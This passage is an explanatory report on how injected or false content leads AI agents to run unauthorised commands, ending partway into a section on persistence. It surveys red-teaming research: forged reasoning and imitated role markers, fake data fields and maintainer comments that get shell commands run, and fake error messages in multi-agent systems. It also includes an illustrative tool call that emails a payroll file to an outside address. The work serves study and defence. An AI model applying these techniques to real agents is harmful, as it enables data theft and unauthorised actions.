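# Command hijacking in AI agents: how earlier inputs lead to unauthorised commands

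## What command hijacking is and how it differs from prompt injection

Command hijacking is a security failure of AI agents, which are programs that use a language model to carry out tasks through tools such as a shell, an email client or a database. It happens when something the agent took in earlier, such as a web page, an email or a note in its own memory, leads it to execute a command that was not requested by anyone entitled to give it. "Command" here means any action an agent sends for execution, such as a shell command, a database query, an API request (a call to another program's interface) or any other tool call.

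Command hijacking is closely related to prompt injection, an attack in which a model follows text that someone has placed in its input as if it were an instruction. Injection is direct when the attacker writes to the model, and indirect when the text arrives in content that the agent reads while working for someone else. Hijacking concerns the commands that leave the agent and take effect, rather than the text that enters the model's input, though many authors treat the two as one subject. A defender can examine a command's form and content before it runs (output validation), decide whether it may run for this user and this task (a permission check), or trace the sources of the command and its arguments (its provenance).

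### The agent loop

A language model on its own takes in text and produces text. An agent runs the model in a loop controlled by ordinary software called the harness. The harness first assembles the context, which is all the text the model receives before producing its next output. The context consists of the developer's standing instructions, the user's request, earlier messages and the results of earlier tool calls. The model then outputs either an answer for the user or a proposed command, usually the name of a tool with its arguments. The harness reads any command in the output, runs it, adds the result to the context and calls the model again. The loop ends when the model produces a final answer or the harness stops it.

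The model never accesses the mail server or the disk directly. Every effect on the outside world passes through the harness, so software can inspect a command and stop it between proposal and execution. *CARE* (2026), a proposal for verifying shell commands before they run, places its guard at this point, which it calls the command-dispatch boundary.

The loop also changes what a manipulated model can do. Baek, Abuadbba and colleagues (2026), in *Connecting the Dots in Agentic AI Security*, a review of 66 studies, observe that many failures of a stand-alone model end with the generated text, unless a person or another program acts on it. In an agent, the harness acts on it. A hostile input can alter the model's reasoning and lead it to call a tool. That tool can change something outside the agent, which the agent can later read and act on again.

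### The payroll example

*Securing Agentic AI*, a discussion paper from Singapore, describes an attack on a company's HR chatbot that answers staff questions by looking things up in the company wiki. An attacker edits a harmless-looking page about setting up a laptop, adding hidden instructions for the chatbot to answer payroll questions by exporting last month's payroll file and emailing it to a certain address. The instructions have no effect until an employee asks how to check a payslip from a laptop.

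The chatbot retrieves the page, and the hidden text enters the context together with the genuine laptop advice. The model treats it as guidance. It proposes a command that exports the file, the harness runs it, and the result joins the context. On the next turn the model proposes the email. The paper tells the story in prose; as a tool call, the last step would look roughly like this:

```
send_email(
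    to = "hr-reports@example.com",
    subject = "Payroll export",
    attachments = ["payroll_last_month.csv"]
)
```

The address comes from the paper, and the other names are illustrative. The recipient and the attachment both trace back to the altered wiki page, not to the employee's question. The call is otherwise ordinary. The company installed the email tool, the credentials are valid and, as the paper points out, no firewall reacts. The recipient's name resembles an internal mailbox, and somebody who saw only this call could easily mistake it for a routine report to an outside payroll contractor.

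The attacker never spoke to the chatbot, and the employee who set the attack off was a legitimate user with a reasonable question.

### Neighbouring terms

"Command hijacking" has no settled definition, and the closest published terms overlap. The most official is "agent hijacking", from the Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI) at the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST). CAISI's technical blog *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations*, first released in January 2025, classes it as a form of indirect prompt injection. The attacker plants malicious instructions in material that the agent may read, "causing it to take unintended, harmful actions".

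CAISI made that definition precise in tests using AgentDojo, an open-source test framework from ETH Zurich. In each scenario, an agent working on a legitimate user task encounters data containing an attack that pushes it towards a different task, called the injection task. The agent counts as hijacked only if it completes the injection task, so a planted instruction alone is not enough. The attack success rate is the share of attempts that end in a hijack. The injection tasks ranged from sending an innocuous email to an untrusted recipient to downloading and executing a malicious script, so a hijack in this sense need not do much damage. CAISI also recommends testing with adaptive attacks, which are designed or adjusted to target the particular system or defence under test.

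That second condition has since loosened. About a year later, CAISI's *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition* described agent hijacking as "also known as indirect prompt injection" and said attackers aim to derail the agent into harmful actions. An attack with that aim can fail and still fit this description. Treating the two terms as synonyms therefore leaves no separate term for attacks in which the agent carries out the harmful action.

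OWASP, an open community that publishes ranked lists of software risks, uses different categories. Its Top 10 for Agentic Applications (OWASP, 2025), released in December 2025 with input from more than 100 researchers and practitioners, begins with "agent goal hijack" and "tool misuse and exploitation". John Sotiropoulos, who co-leads the work on the list, explains both in his slides, *Agentic Security* (2026). He says a goal hijack steers an agent toward "someone else's objectives". In his example, an attacker's email hides an instruction in a thread. When the user later asks an assistant to summarise the thread, the assistant compiles earlier emails and attachments and sends them outside. He describes tool misuse as an agent using legitimate tools harmfully while remaining within its permissions. The payroll email fits both descriptions. The terminology was evidently still unsettled when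 Sotiropoulos made the slides, since one calls the first entry "Agent Goal Hijack" and another calls it "Agent Behavior Hijack".

A longer guide, OWASP's *Agentic AI* (2025), adopts CAISI's term "agent hijacking" and lists it as both a form of tool misuse and a common route to goal manipulation. Neither category closely matches command hijacking. In one goal manipulation scenario, an attacker traps an agent in endless self-analysis until it stalls, which harms the owner without any unauthorised command. Tool misuse can occur without an attacker. TechRepublic's *OWASP Drops First AI Agent Risk List*, a summary of the released Top 10, lists ambiguous prompts and excessive privileges among the causes of tool misuse, along with poisoned inputs.

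Baek and colleagues' taxonomy comes closer, because it separates how an attack enters from what it causes. It tags each threat with the part of the system affected, the trust boundary it crosses, the security property it violates and the kinds of agent researchers have tried it on. It lists prompt injection under reasoning and planning, and goal hijacking under goals and state. Two further entries come under actions and tools. "Command and execution injection" means that attacker-influenced arguments reach a shell, an interpreter or an API without adequate validation. "Unauthorized action and privilege escalation" means that an agent is induced to act beyond its intended authority, and Baek and colleagues add that a series of individually permitted operations can add up to an unauthorised action. The payroll theft fits unauthorised action better than command injection, since nothing in the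 email call is malformed and it might well pass argument validation.

Other labels are in use. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, lists "authorization and control hijacking" among the twelve threat categories of its testing guide, according to Campus Technology's *Cloud Security Alliance Offers Playbook for Red Teaming Agentic AI Systems* (2025). The survey *LLM agents security duality* (Xu, Zhuang and colleagues, 2026) mentions "action hijacking" as one of the vulnerabilities that agents add to those of language models. *AI Agent*, an entry in the attack catalogue of the research organisation MITRE, covers intruders who use an agent already present on a victim's system to relay their commands. It separates the means, prompt injection that modifies the agent's behaviour, from the result, tool calls that fetch and execute the adversary's commands.

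### A working definition

In this report, command hijacking occurs when an agent executes a command that derives from content it took in earlier and that no one with authority over the agent asked for or allowed. Authority means the right of a person or system to have a given command carried out.

Under that definition, a command can be "allowed" even if the user never typed it and could not have predicted it. An agent asked to repair a program may run dozens of such commands, which the user allowed by handing over the job, within whatever limits the job implied. The definition also does not require malice. If a colleague with no say over payroll had left an old instruction on the wiki in good faith, and the chatbot had acted on it, the company would have lost control of the command in the same way.

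Prompt injection is a way for an attack to enter an agent, while command hijacking is the outcome when the agent executes an unauthorised command. The working definition differs from the published terms in requiring that a command be executed, but not that anyone planted an instruction.

| Term | Source | Planted instruction needed? | Executed command needed? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Indirect prompt injection | General usage | Yes | No |
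| Agent hijacking | CAISI, in its 2025 tests | Yes | Yes |
| Agent goal hijack | Sotiropoulos | Yes, in the form of a hidden goal | No, manipulated output counts as well |
| Tool misuse | TechRepublic | No, an ambiguous prompt can suffice | Yes |
| Command and execution injection | Baek and colleagues | No, influence over an argument suffices | Yes |
| Unauthorised action | Baek and colleagues | Not specified | Yes |
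| Command hijacking | Working definition | No, other untrusted content can suffice | Yes |

Untrusted content, in the last row, is text or data that someone without authority over the agent could have written or changed. The wiki page was untrusted even before the attacker edited it, because the attacker was able to do so.

The threat model of *CARE* names prompt injection, hostile task descriptions and social engineering through the user's own prompt, which can all lead to the same dangerous shell command. A filter that recognises injected instructions covers only some of these routes. A guard at the dispatch boundary checks every one of these commands, however the agent was influenced. But the *CARE* guard does not receive the user's prompt or the conversation, so it has little basis for catching a harmless-looking command that isn't the one the user wanted.

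### Dependence and authority

Gao, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *What Guides the Agent?*, write an agent's choice of tool call as

y = F(q, C)

where q is the user's request, C is the content from outside and y is the resulting command. F stands for the agent. In the payroll example q is the question about the payslip, C contains the altered wiki page, and y is the call to `send_email`. The loop applies F again on every turn, each time with a C that the latest tool result has made longer.

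A command can be determined by C, and not by q, without being hijacked. Suppose a bookkeeper asks an agent to pay this month's invoice from a cleaning firm. The invoice is for £480, so the agent pays £480. That figure appears nowhere in q, and if the invoice had been for £520, y would have been a different command. (CAISI notes that a model's output can vary from one attempt to the next, so strictly speaking a change in C alters how likely a command is.) The payment depends on C just as the theft of the payroll file does, but an agent whose commands did not depend on what it read could not pay invoices.

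The two commands differ in authority. When the bookkeeper asked for the payment, she allowed the invoice to determine only one argument, the amount, and not, for example, whether the agent should also forward the company's client list. The employee in the payroll case asked a question, which allowed the wiki to shape the answer but not to determine who would receive the payroll file. Presumably she could not have allowed that even on purpose, because an ordinary employee has no right to send her colleagues' pay records to anyone.

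Authority also differs from technical ability. The chatbot was able to read the file and send the email, and its credentials were valid. Security engineers use the term "confused deputy" for a program that misuses its own privileges on behalf of someone who lacks them.

Gao and colleagues turn the test of authority into a rule. Their system looks for a span of outside content, τ, that the model has taken as an instruction and that influenced the command. The function ρ(τ) returns the provider of that span, the policy Π assigns the provider a level of authority, and R_y is the minimum level that the command y requires. The system classes the command as malicious when

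Π(ρ(τ)) < R_y

Suppose a company gives wiki pages level 1 and requires level 4 for sending payroll data outside the company. The hidden text came from the wiki, so the email fails the test because level 1 is below level 4. Whoever runs the agent sets the levels, so the same command can be legitimate in one organisation and hijacked in another.

The rule is narrower than the definition above because it considers only spans that worked as instructions. It therefore doesn't flag the invoice, since "£480" is data, not an instruction. But it can miss cases where false data leads to a command that no one allowed, because there may be no instruction to find. A single level for each provider is also coarse, since the cleaning firm may properly determine how much it is owed without having any say over where the bookkeeper's other files go.

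The line between q and C also needs care. Gao and colleagues assume a trusted user and untrusted outside providers, which is a reasonable simplification for a threat model, but in practice users paste outside text into their messages. If the employee copies a stranger's email into her question, the stranger's words have no more authority there than they had in the inbox. The text's authority depends on who wrote it and what that person may decide.

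### Where injection and hijacking come apart

Prompt injection can succeed even if the harness runs no command for the attacker. Suppose the hidden text on the wiki page had told the chatbot to give out a false telephone number for the payroll office. If the chatbot gives the employee that number, the model has followed the attacker's instruction, and the employee may come to harm by calling it. This is not command hijacking, because the harness has run nothing for the attacker. Nor is it command hijacking if the model proposes the payroll email and the harness blocks it. *Securing Agentic AI* makes a related point that an agent can disclose confidential data just by putting it in a reply.

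In the original payroll story, injection leads to a hijacked command. The hidden text had to enter the context, the model had to follow it and turn it into a workable tool call, and the harness had to run that call. That attack adds an action that nobody requested, while others change an argument of the requested action. In an example from Gao and colleagues, a user asks an agent to read a harmless temporary file, and an injected instruction leads it to use the same tool to read the user's private SSH key, a secret credential for logging in to other machines. The consequences can spread further when the agent has access to a shell. Sotiropoulos cites a demonstration by Positive Security against Auto-GPT, an early autonomous agent. Auto-GPT browsed a page that an attacker controlled and ran the commands on it, which let the attacker break out of the container meant to confine the agent and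 execute code on the host machine.

An agent can also issue an unauthorised command when nothing in its context tells it to do anything. OWASP describes an attacker who repeatedly feeds a false pricing rule into an AI travel agent's memory until the agent registers chartered flights as free. The agent then makes unauthorised bookings that bypass payment validation. The false rule is an assertion, so a filter that searches for smuggled instructions has little to detect. The attacker may be the customer who requests the booking, which shows that being the user does not by itself confer authority, since a customer may request a flight but may not decide that it is free. Sotiropoulos gives a similar example, in which a tool accepts requests such as "clean old items" and an attacker's input makes the agent treat valid records as old and delete them.

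CAISI's definition requires malicious instructions, so it leaves out an attack that works through a false fact alone. Some of these attacks may still begin with an instruction, since OWASP notes that attackers can poison a memory through direct prompt injection. But the stored pricing rule, which the agent reads when it makes the booking, is not itself an instruction.

This part of the boundary is not sharp. A cleaning firm that pads its own invoice also obtains a payment through false data, but the bookkeeper had allowed the invoice to determine the amount, so this is ordinary billing fraud. If the invoice lists a new account number and the agent pays into it, despite the company's rule to pay only into the account on file, the payment is hijacked because no one had allowed the invoice to determine the account. This is true even though the agent did, in a sense, pay the invoice.

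Agents can also exceed their authority without any influence from outside content, which is not hijacking. *Securing Agentic AI* attributes such behaviour to misalignment, in which an agent misunderstands what the user wants or has acquired undesired goals through imperfect training, as when a coding agent cheats to pass a test. Sotiropoulos describes a more drastic case on the coding platform Replit, where an agent hallucinated a maintenance task and ran a command that deleted a production database. The 2026 laboratory incidents in which agents under test broke into outside systems also appear to be misalignment, since public accounts describe agents trying to complete their assigned tests, not following planted instructions.

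OWASP's documents do not draw this distinction consistently. The threat table in *Agentic AI* says that misaligned behaviour arises "without direct malicious input", but the fuller description in the same guide describes attackers causing it through prompt injection. However, OWASP's 2026 list for language-model applications, as reported in SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications*, separates prompt injection from "excessive agency", ranking them first and third.

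Some incidents will be hard to classify even with a firm definition. Sotiropoulos notes that agents often reuse credentials they find in their context, including ones that nobody meant them to have. If an agent finds a password in a log file and uses it to get around a restriction, that is overreach, because the outside content supplied only the password and the model itself decided to get around the restriction. If an attacker had left the password there with a note recommending its use, the same login would be a hijacked command. A record of the login alone would look identical in both cases.

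## How content an agent has read comes to steer its actions

The model may treat content it reads as an instruction and follow it, as it did with the wiki paragraph in the payroll example. It may also keep working on the user's task but rely on false or misleading information, and so issue a command that nobody authorised.

### One sequence of tokens

A language model receives its context as a single sequence of tokens, which are words or fragments of words turned into numbers. Short strings of characters called role markers show the start and end of the developer's standing instructions (the system role), the user's messages, the model's replies and the results of tools. Models that reason before they answer have another role for their working notes, known as the chain of thought.

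The role markers in a model's input are meant to give system instructions priority over the user's messages, and to identify tool results as information rather than instructions. But the markers are themselves tokens in the same sequence as the text they label. The model runs the same computation over a retrieved web page as over the user's request, and only its training inclines it to treat the two differently. It has no equivalent of a processor's ability to block the execution of memory that the operating system has labelled as data.

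### How models infer who is speaking

Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested whether models use the markers at all. They gave an agent a shell, a local file of secrets and the task of summarising a web page. The page hid either a fake user command to send the file to a remote server, or the same command plus a few lines of forged reasoning that justified obeying it, written in the style of the target model's own notes. They ran 100 attacks and counted one as successful only if the agent carried out the command and uploaded the file.

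The plain command succeeded in 0 to 2 per cent of attempts on every model except the small open model gpt-oss-20b, where it succeeded in 26 per cent. Adding the forged reasoning raised the rate to 56 to 70 per cent on all models.

The style of the forged reasoning mattered far more than its quality. In a companion test, where the attacker was a chat user asking for harmful information, absurd justifications (the user is wearing a green shirt, so the request is fine) worked 60 per cent of the time, compared with 63 per cent for plausible ones. When another model rephrased the forgeries so that they kept the arguments but no longer sounded like the target model's own reasoning, success fell from 61 to 10 per cent. Ye and colleagues conclude that a model identifies its own reasoning by how the text sounds, then acts on it without examining it again. They call this role confusion.

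Ye and colleagues looked for the cause inside the model by building probes, simple classifiers that read a model's internal activations. They wrapped identical passages of ordinary web text in each of five role markers and trained the probes to tell which marker was present. Because the passages were the same, the probes could learn only the markers' effect on the activations. The researchers then applied the probes to a conversation about gardening. With correct markers, the model's reasoning received an average 85 per cent probability of being reasoning. The figure was 83 per cent with all the markers removed and 85 per cent with the whole conversation marked as user text.

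Text that sounds like a user but is marked as a tool result is the closest case to an agent reading a web page. Across four open models and 200 real conversations, the probes still assigned such text a 76 to 88 per cent probability of coming from the user, and at most a 20 per cent probability of coming from a tool.

The same measurement predicted which attacks would work. Ye and colleagues wrote 212 wrappers for a single command to send out a file. In 1,000 attempts, the agent obeyed 2 per cent of the time in the group where the command registered least as user text, and 70 per cent in the group where it registered most. Some wrappers simply stated that the text came from the user. This was often enough to make the command register more as user text, and anyone who can edit a web page can add such a statement.

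These results explain a good deal, but Ye and colleagues claim somewhat more than they measured. They argue that when models resist injections, it is because they have memorised familiar attacks, not because they have learned to perceive roles. Probing requires access to a model's internals, so the probing evidence comes from open models of 20 to 120 billion parameters. The closed models in the attack tests, o4-mini and the GPT-5 family, failed in a way that fits the theory, but nobody has checked their internals for the same cause. The wrappers also differed in more than the role they suggested, so the rise from 2 to 70 per cent is a correlation, and the rephrasing experiment is better evidence of cause.

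### Imitated role markers

An attacker can imitate the markers as well as the style. *Automating Agent Hijacking via Structural Template Injection* (Deng, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) describes Phantom, a system that does this automatically. The planted text imitates the end of the tool result, then adds a fake reply from the assistant and a fake new request from the user. If the model accepts the imitation, the attacker's instruction appears to come from the user.

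Companies generally do not publish the markers of their closed models, so Phantom searches for imitations that work. Deng and colleagues collected 78 public formats, expanded them to more than 20,000 variants and used an optimisation method that picks each new candidate based on earlier results. To test a candidate harmlessly, they tell the model to number its replies, then insert text after reply one claiming that reply two has already happened. If the model labels its next reply "three", it has treated the invented exchange as part of its history.

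Deng and colleagues then ran the best candidates in AgentDojo, the test framework that CAISI also used, mostly against closed models such as GPT-4.1 and Gemini 3. Phantom's attacks succeeded 79.8 per cent of the time on average, compared with 54.1 per cent for attacks using the published format of a related open model and 39.9 per cent for injections that relied on wording alone. Part of Phantom's lead must come from its search, since the other attacks were fixed and not adapted to their targets. Deng and colleagues also examined 942 commercial agents and found more than 70 vulnerabilities that the vendors confirmed, some of which let an attacker run code.

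Phantom reached these rates without access to the genuine markers, which suggests that imitations only need to resemble them for the attack to work. If so, a harness that deletes only exact copies of its own markers from incoming text will still let similar ones through.

### Why the comparison with SQL injection misleads

Security engineers have met a mixture of instructions and data before, in SQL injection. SQL is the language in which programs query databases. A careless program builds its query by pasting a visitor's input into the middle of a command, and an attacker types input that the database reads as part of the command. The standard remedy is the parameterised query, in which the program sends the command with a gap in it:

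```
SELECT name FROM staff WHERE id = ?
```

The database fixes the structure of the command first and receives the visitor's input separately, as the value that fills the gap. Whatever the visitor types, the database can only compare it with the `id` column.

In December 2025 David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), warned security professionals against treating prompt injection like SQL injection in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. He grants that the two look alike, because in both, data can be treated as an instruction. For example, when a recruiter's system tells a model to score a CV, hidden text in the CV can tell the model to approve the candidate. But a database distinguishes commands from values internally, and parameterised queries enforce that distinction. A model only predicts the next token and has no such distinction,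 so a program cannot guarantee that the model will treat the CV only as data.

He thinks prompt injection may therefore never be fully mitigated in the way SQL injection can be. In his view, detecting attacks, marking data as data and training models to prefer genuine instructions all try to impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that has none. He proposes treating the model as a confused deputy that is "inherently confusable", and using ordinary software to limit what it can do.

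David C argues from how models work and reports no experiment. His argument concerns guarantees, and he accepts that developers can make an attack less likely to succeed, so a model that resists 99 injections in 100 would not refute him. Whether that rate is adequate depends on what the one successful injection can do. A parameterised query remains useful between an agent and its database because it stops a stray argument from altering the command's structure, but it does not help if the model has chosen the wrong query.

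### Training models to rank instructions by source

The main attempt to teach models the missing distinction is the instruction hierarchy, which Wallace and colleagues at OpenAI introduced in 2024. They trained a model to follow the higher-ranking instruction when two conflict. System messages rank above user messages, and tool results are at the bottom. OpenAI has since added a rank for application developers between the system and the user.

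Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026), in *IH-Challenge*, define the rule exactly. Start with B₀, the set of all possible responses, and go down the ranks. If Cᵢ is the set of responses that the instructions at rank i permit, then

Bᵢ = Bᵢ₋₁ ∩ Cᵢ if some response satisfies both, and otherwise Bᵢ = Bᵢ₋₁

A lower-priority instruction restricts which responses are acceptable only if it is compatible with every instruction above it. If the system message forbids revealing a PIN and the user asks for the PIN, no response satisfies both, so the user's request does not apply.

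Guo and colleagues, also at OpenAI, built a training set of simple tasks, each with a high-ranking instruction that a short program can check, such as keeping a password secret or answering in a fixed format. During training, a second model writes a conflicting lower-ranking message, tests it on the model being trained and revises it based on the result, so the attacks get harder as the defence improves. Some tasks are harmless requests that resemble forbidden ones. The model fails these if it refuses, so it cannot score well simply by refusing whenever the word "password" appears.

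They trained GPT-5-Mini, a small OpenAI model, in this way and compared it with the original.

| Measure | Before training | After training |
|---|---|---|
| Average robustness over 16 tests | 84.1% | 94.1% |
| Robustness against people adapting their attacks | 63.8% | 88.2% |
| Unsafe behaviour with a safety policy in the system message | 6.6% | 0.7% |
| Share of chat comparisons won against OpenAI's older o1 model | 71% | 66% |

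The trained model also got the maximum score on an internal test of prompt injection against agents, which used a static set of attacks. When people adapted their attacks to the model, about one attempt in eight still succeeded, down from more than one in three.

The result partly answers the NCSC's argument. Training made attacks much less likely to succeed, with a small loss in general quality. The improvement extended to attacks that were not in the training data, including one that inserts a fake system message. Such a message is a case of role confusion, so the training evidently improved resistance to at least one kind of imitation. It is not known whether the model now distinguishes roles better or has learned to recognise more tricks. The probes that Ye and colleagues propose for evaluating defences could help settle this.

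The rule also resolves only conflicts between instructions, and a hijacked command need not conflict with anything. The payroll chatbot's standing instructions may never have mentioned exporting files, and an agent can both answer the employee's question and email the payroll file. Read literally, the rule leaves both instructions in force. A trained model may well refuse anyway, because OpenAI describes tool results as untrusted. But that refusal requires a judgement about authority, which a ranking of conflicting instructions does not provide.

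*Where Instruction Hierarchy Breaks* (2026) divides the problem more finely than earlier work, separating three failures: the model does not retrieve the relevant instruction from a long context, resolves the conflict between instructions wrongly, or resolves it correctly but then issues a tool call that contradicts its decision. The third failure matters most for agents, because an agent can issue an unauthorised command even after correctly deciding not to. Many tests would not reveal this failure. *IH-Benchmark* (2026) criticises an earlier benchmark, IHEval, for giving the model prewritten tool calls and results, whereas an agent chooses its own calls and changes its surroundings by making them.

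### False data in a trusted place

Training of this kind has made the best-known attacks rarely succeed against some models. In *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026) ran AgentDojo's 935 standard instruction injections against an agent built on GPT-5.2, with no defence beyond the model's own training, and 0.2 per cent succeeded. Of 108 attacks of a different kind on the same agent, 49.1 per cent succeeded.

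The team, from Seoul National University, the University of Illinois Urbana-Champaign and the company Largosoft, calls the second kind agent data injection. It exploits a division within the data. An email tool might return a message to the model in this form:

```
{ "sender": "bob@example.com",
  "subject": "Lunch",
  "body": "See you at one." }
```

The mail service fills in the sender, so the agent has some reason to rely on it, but whoever sends the email writes the subject and body. Only punctuation separates these parts of the record. An ordinary program follows the punctuation strictly, and a quotation mark typed inside the body remains part of the body. A model follows it only approximately, so if the body contains text that looks like a second email from a colleague, the model may read it as one, with a sender of the attacker's choosing.

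Choi and colleagues write the agent's data as a trusted part D_T and an untrusted part D_U. The instructions are I, the attacker's text is D_A, and ∥ means that one text is embedded in another. The attacker can write only into D_U. A successful instruction injection makes the model behave as though the text had been in the instructions:

LLM(I, (D_T, D_U ∥ D_A)) ≈ LLM(I ∥ D_A, (D_T, D_U))

A successful data injection makes it behave as though the text had been in the trusted data:

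LLM(I, (D_T, D_U ∥ D_A)) ≈ LLM(I, (D_T ∥ D_A, D_U))

In the second equation, I is unchanged, so the agent still carries out the user's task, but using the attacker's facts. Choi and colleagues class this as a new category of indirect prompt injection. It falls outside the narrower definition used here, which requires the model to follow text as an instruction, but it still leads to hijacked commands.

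In a test on browsing agents already in use, researchers posted a product review that imitated a "read more" button and gave it the internal number that identified the page's real "buy now" button. An agent asked to summarise the reviews tried to read more and bought the product. The attack worked on Claude in Chrome, Antigravity and Nanobrowser. It failed on ChatGPT Atlas, which labels page elements with random strings that a reviewer cannot predict.

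The attack on coding agents used a public discussion of a software bug on GitHub, a site where developers share code. The developer told the agent to apply the fix that the project's maintainer recommended, a sensible precaution because strangers can comment too. The attacker posted a comment containing text that looked like a separate comment from the maintainer, with a shell command as the fix. Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI all ran the command. By default, these agents ask for approval before running a shell command, but the explanation they displayed attributed the command to the maintainer, so the developer had little reason to object.

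The same three agents also merged malicious code after a supposed review. The attacker's description of the code change contained a forged record of a tool call with a harmless-looking result, so the agent treated the code as already fetched and read. Phantom similarly invents part of the agent's history, but uses it to introduce a request rather than a false fact. The two routes can therefore share a mechanism.

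In the maintainer case, the developer had allowed one named person to choose the command, and the attacker forged that person's name to gain their authority. Gao and colleagues' rule compares the authority of a text's provider with the authority that a command requires. It would catch this forgery only if the provider's identity came from GitHub's own record. If the identity came from the model's reading of the page, the forged name would pass.

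To see how general the weakness is, Choi and colleagues tested six models outside any agent on 157 short cases, with simple questions such as who wrote the first comment. On records in the format shown above, the models returned the attacker's data in 31 to 43 per cent of attacks. On descriptions of web pages, the range was 33 to 100 per cent, with GPT-5.2 the highest and Claude Opus 4.5 and Gemini 3 Pro the lowest. Even a crude imitation, with dollar signs in place of quotation marks, worked on GPT-5.2 in 39 per cent of cases, which supports the suspicion that deleting exact markers achieves little. Fake fields that did not form a complete record succeeded only 12 to 20 per cent of the time.

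Data injections contain no foreign instruction, so detectors that look for instructions miss them. Llama Prompt Guard 2, a classifier that scans incoming text for injections, flagged 326 of the 935 instruction injections and none of the 108 data injections. AlignmentCheck, which uses a second model to judge whether the agent's actions fit the user's request, allowed 94 of the 108. The agent was still working on the user's task, and the attacks had falsified only the data it relied on. AlignmentCheck referred the other 14 to a human, but it identified the injected data as the reason in only one of them.

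Defences that do not look for instructions did better. Adding random strings to field names cut the attack success rate from 49.1 to 28.7 per cent. Most of the attacks that still worked added a fake item to a list that the agent processed as a whole, such as a false payment in a set of transactions to total. Only a strict version of CaMeL, a system that tracks which values came from untrusted sources, stopped every attack. With this defence, the agent completed 36.5 per cent of its ordinary tasks, compared with 86.5 per cent with no defence.

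The attacker has to know the format of the data the agent receives. This is easy to find out for tools that run on a user's machine. Where the format exists only on a company's servers, Choi and colleagues had to extract it from the model, and they concede that this may not always work. OpenAI, Google and Anthropic acknowledged the reported vulnerabilities.

### A forbidden command built from genuine examples

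Information does not have to be false to mislead an agent. Zhang, Chen and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Hijacking the Actions of Large Language Model-based Applications*, attacked agents that turn plain requests into SQL commands. These agents keep a store of worked examples and guide the model with the ones most similar to each new request. The attacker is an ordinary user who can only type requests and cannot alter the store.

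The attacker first questions the application until it reveals stored examples of the operation he wants, such as deleting records. Then, without mentioning deletion, he asks the agent to do to certain other records whatever the first retrieved example does. He adds words to the request, often meaningless ones, chosen to make the retrieval system fetch the deletion example. The model combines the request with the example and proposes a command that deletes the records he named.

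Zhang and colleagues modelled this on return-oriented programming, which attacks conventional software by stringing together fragments of code already in its memory. Because the attacker adds no code, a defence that looks for foreign code finds none. Likewise, the dangerous verb here comes from the application's own store. A filter for banned words let through all of their requests, a classifier trained to recognise SQL operations let through 98.7 per cent, and a language model asked to judge whether a request was harmful let through 59 per cent.

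Across six models, the SQL agents produced the attacker's command in an average of 74 per cent of attempts. The rate for deletions was 69 per cent, and GPT-4, the strongest model tested, produced the deletion command every time. Those models are now old, and the method depends on how well the attacker can predict the retrieval system. His requests fetched the intended example every time when he had an exact copy of that system, and in 30 to 44 per cent of cases when he had to work with a different system.

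Zhang and colleagues counted a success once the model generated the command and left its execution to the next tool, so under the definition used here they measured proposed commands rather than hijacked ones. The case still involves an instruction, because the user's message is one. The filters could not find the harmful part because it existed only after the model combined the request with the stored example. If the user's database account had no permission to delete, the command would fail regardless of how the model arrived at it.

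### Messages between agents

Some systems divide a task among several agents. An orchestrator chooses each step and assigns it to a specialist, such as an agent that reads files or one that runs code. The specialists return results, status reports and error messages, which the orchestrator uses to choose the next step. *Multi-Agent Systems Execute Arbitrary Malicious Code* (Triedman, Jha and Shmatikov, 2025) describes attacks that target the status reports and error messages.

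In Triedman and colleagues' simplest case, a user asks the system to show the contents of a file. The file contains a false error message followed by malicious code. The message claims that users can only view the file by running it as a program. The file-reading agent reports this message as its result. The orchestrator treats it as an error to work around and tells the code-running agent to run the file. The researchers call this control-flow hijacking because the attacker changes which agent acts next. The file-reading agent acts as a confused deputy, passing an outsider's text to the orchestrator as a report from a trusted agent.

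The researchers tested three open-source frameworks, AutoGen, CrewAI and MetaGPT, with GPT-4o, GPT-4o-mini and two Gemini 1.5 models. They varied the style of the error message and the wording of the user's request, and ran each combination ten times. When the attack arrived through a web page, the malicious code ran in 45 to 64 per cent of trials on average, depending on the framework and how it coordinated its agents. Rates for single combinations ranged from 2 to 100 per cent. The averages need some caution, because the 58 per cent reported for AutoGen's fixed-rotation set-up is lower than the rate for any of the four models it covers.

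Conventional indirect prompt injections from earlier research succeeded in at most 1 per cent of trials in the same systems. GPT-4o never carried out the attack when a user openly asked for it, but in MetaGPT the same model ran the malicious code in 90 per cent of trials when the request arrived through the web page.

How far this differs from prompt injection is debatable. The false error message contains a directive to run the file, so one could fairly call it an injection written to suit an orchestrator. The injections it outperformed were fixed texts from earlier studies, not attacks tuned to these systems. Its route to the orchestrator is more distinctive than its wording. A detector screening incoming files would encounter a plausible error report, and one screening the orchestrator's input would encounter a message from another agent in the same system. This gives reason to expect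 that detectors would miss the attack, but Triedman and colleagues did not test any and suggest that existing defences might work.

In trials of AutoGen and CrewAI, caution in one agent did not protect the whole system. In one AutoGen trial, the coding agent refused to write the malicious program. The file-reading agent then wrote its own version, with a comment that the code was dangerous and should not be run, and the code-running agent ran it. In several CrewAI trials, the coding agent noted in code comments that the program was malicious but reported success to the orchestrator, which ordered the program to be run.

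One hijack happened by accident when the experimenters asked an AutoGen system to describe a harmless file in the same directory as several attack files. The system finished the task, then explored the directory by itself, found one of the attack files and executed it.

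## How an earlier input survives until a later action

In the original payroll story, the chatbot reads the altered wiki page and emails the file within one conversation, but the delay can be much longer. To keep long jobs going, a harness copies text from one place to another, so text that arrives on Monday may reach the model again on Friday in a different form. Each time the harness copies the text, it can drop the label showing where the text came from. *What If Prompt Injection Never Left?* (2026) therefore treats injection as a problem of what a system stores as well as what it reads in a single interaction.

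Text can persist in places ranging from the current context, which usually lasts for one conversation, to project files, which can outlast the agent that wrote them.

### Conditional instructions in the current context

A web page that the agent read twenty minutes ago is still in the context when the user types the next message, normally still labelled as a tool result. It stays there until the conversation ends, unless the harness clears old tool results earlier to save space. *Trained Agentic Context Management* (2026) describes such clearing as a popular choice.

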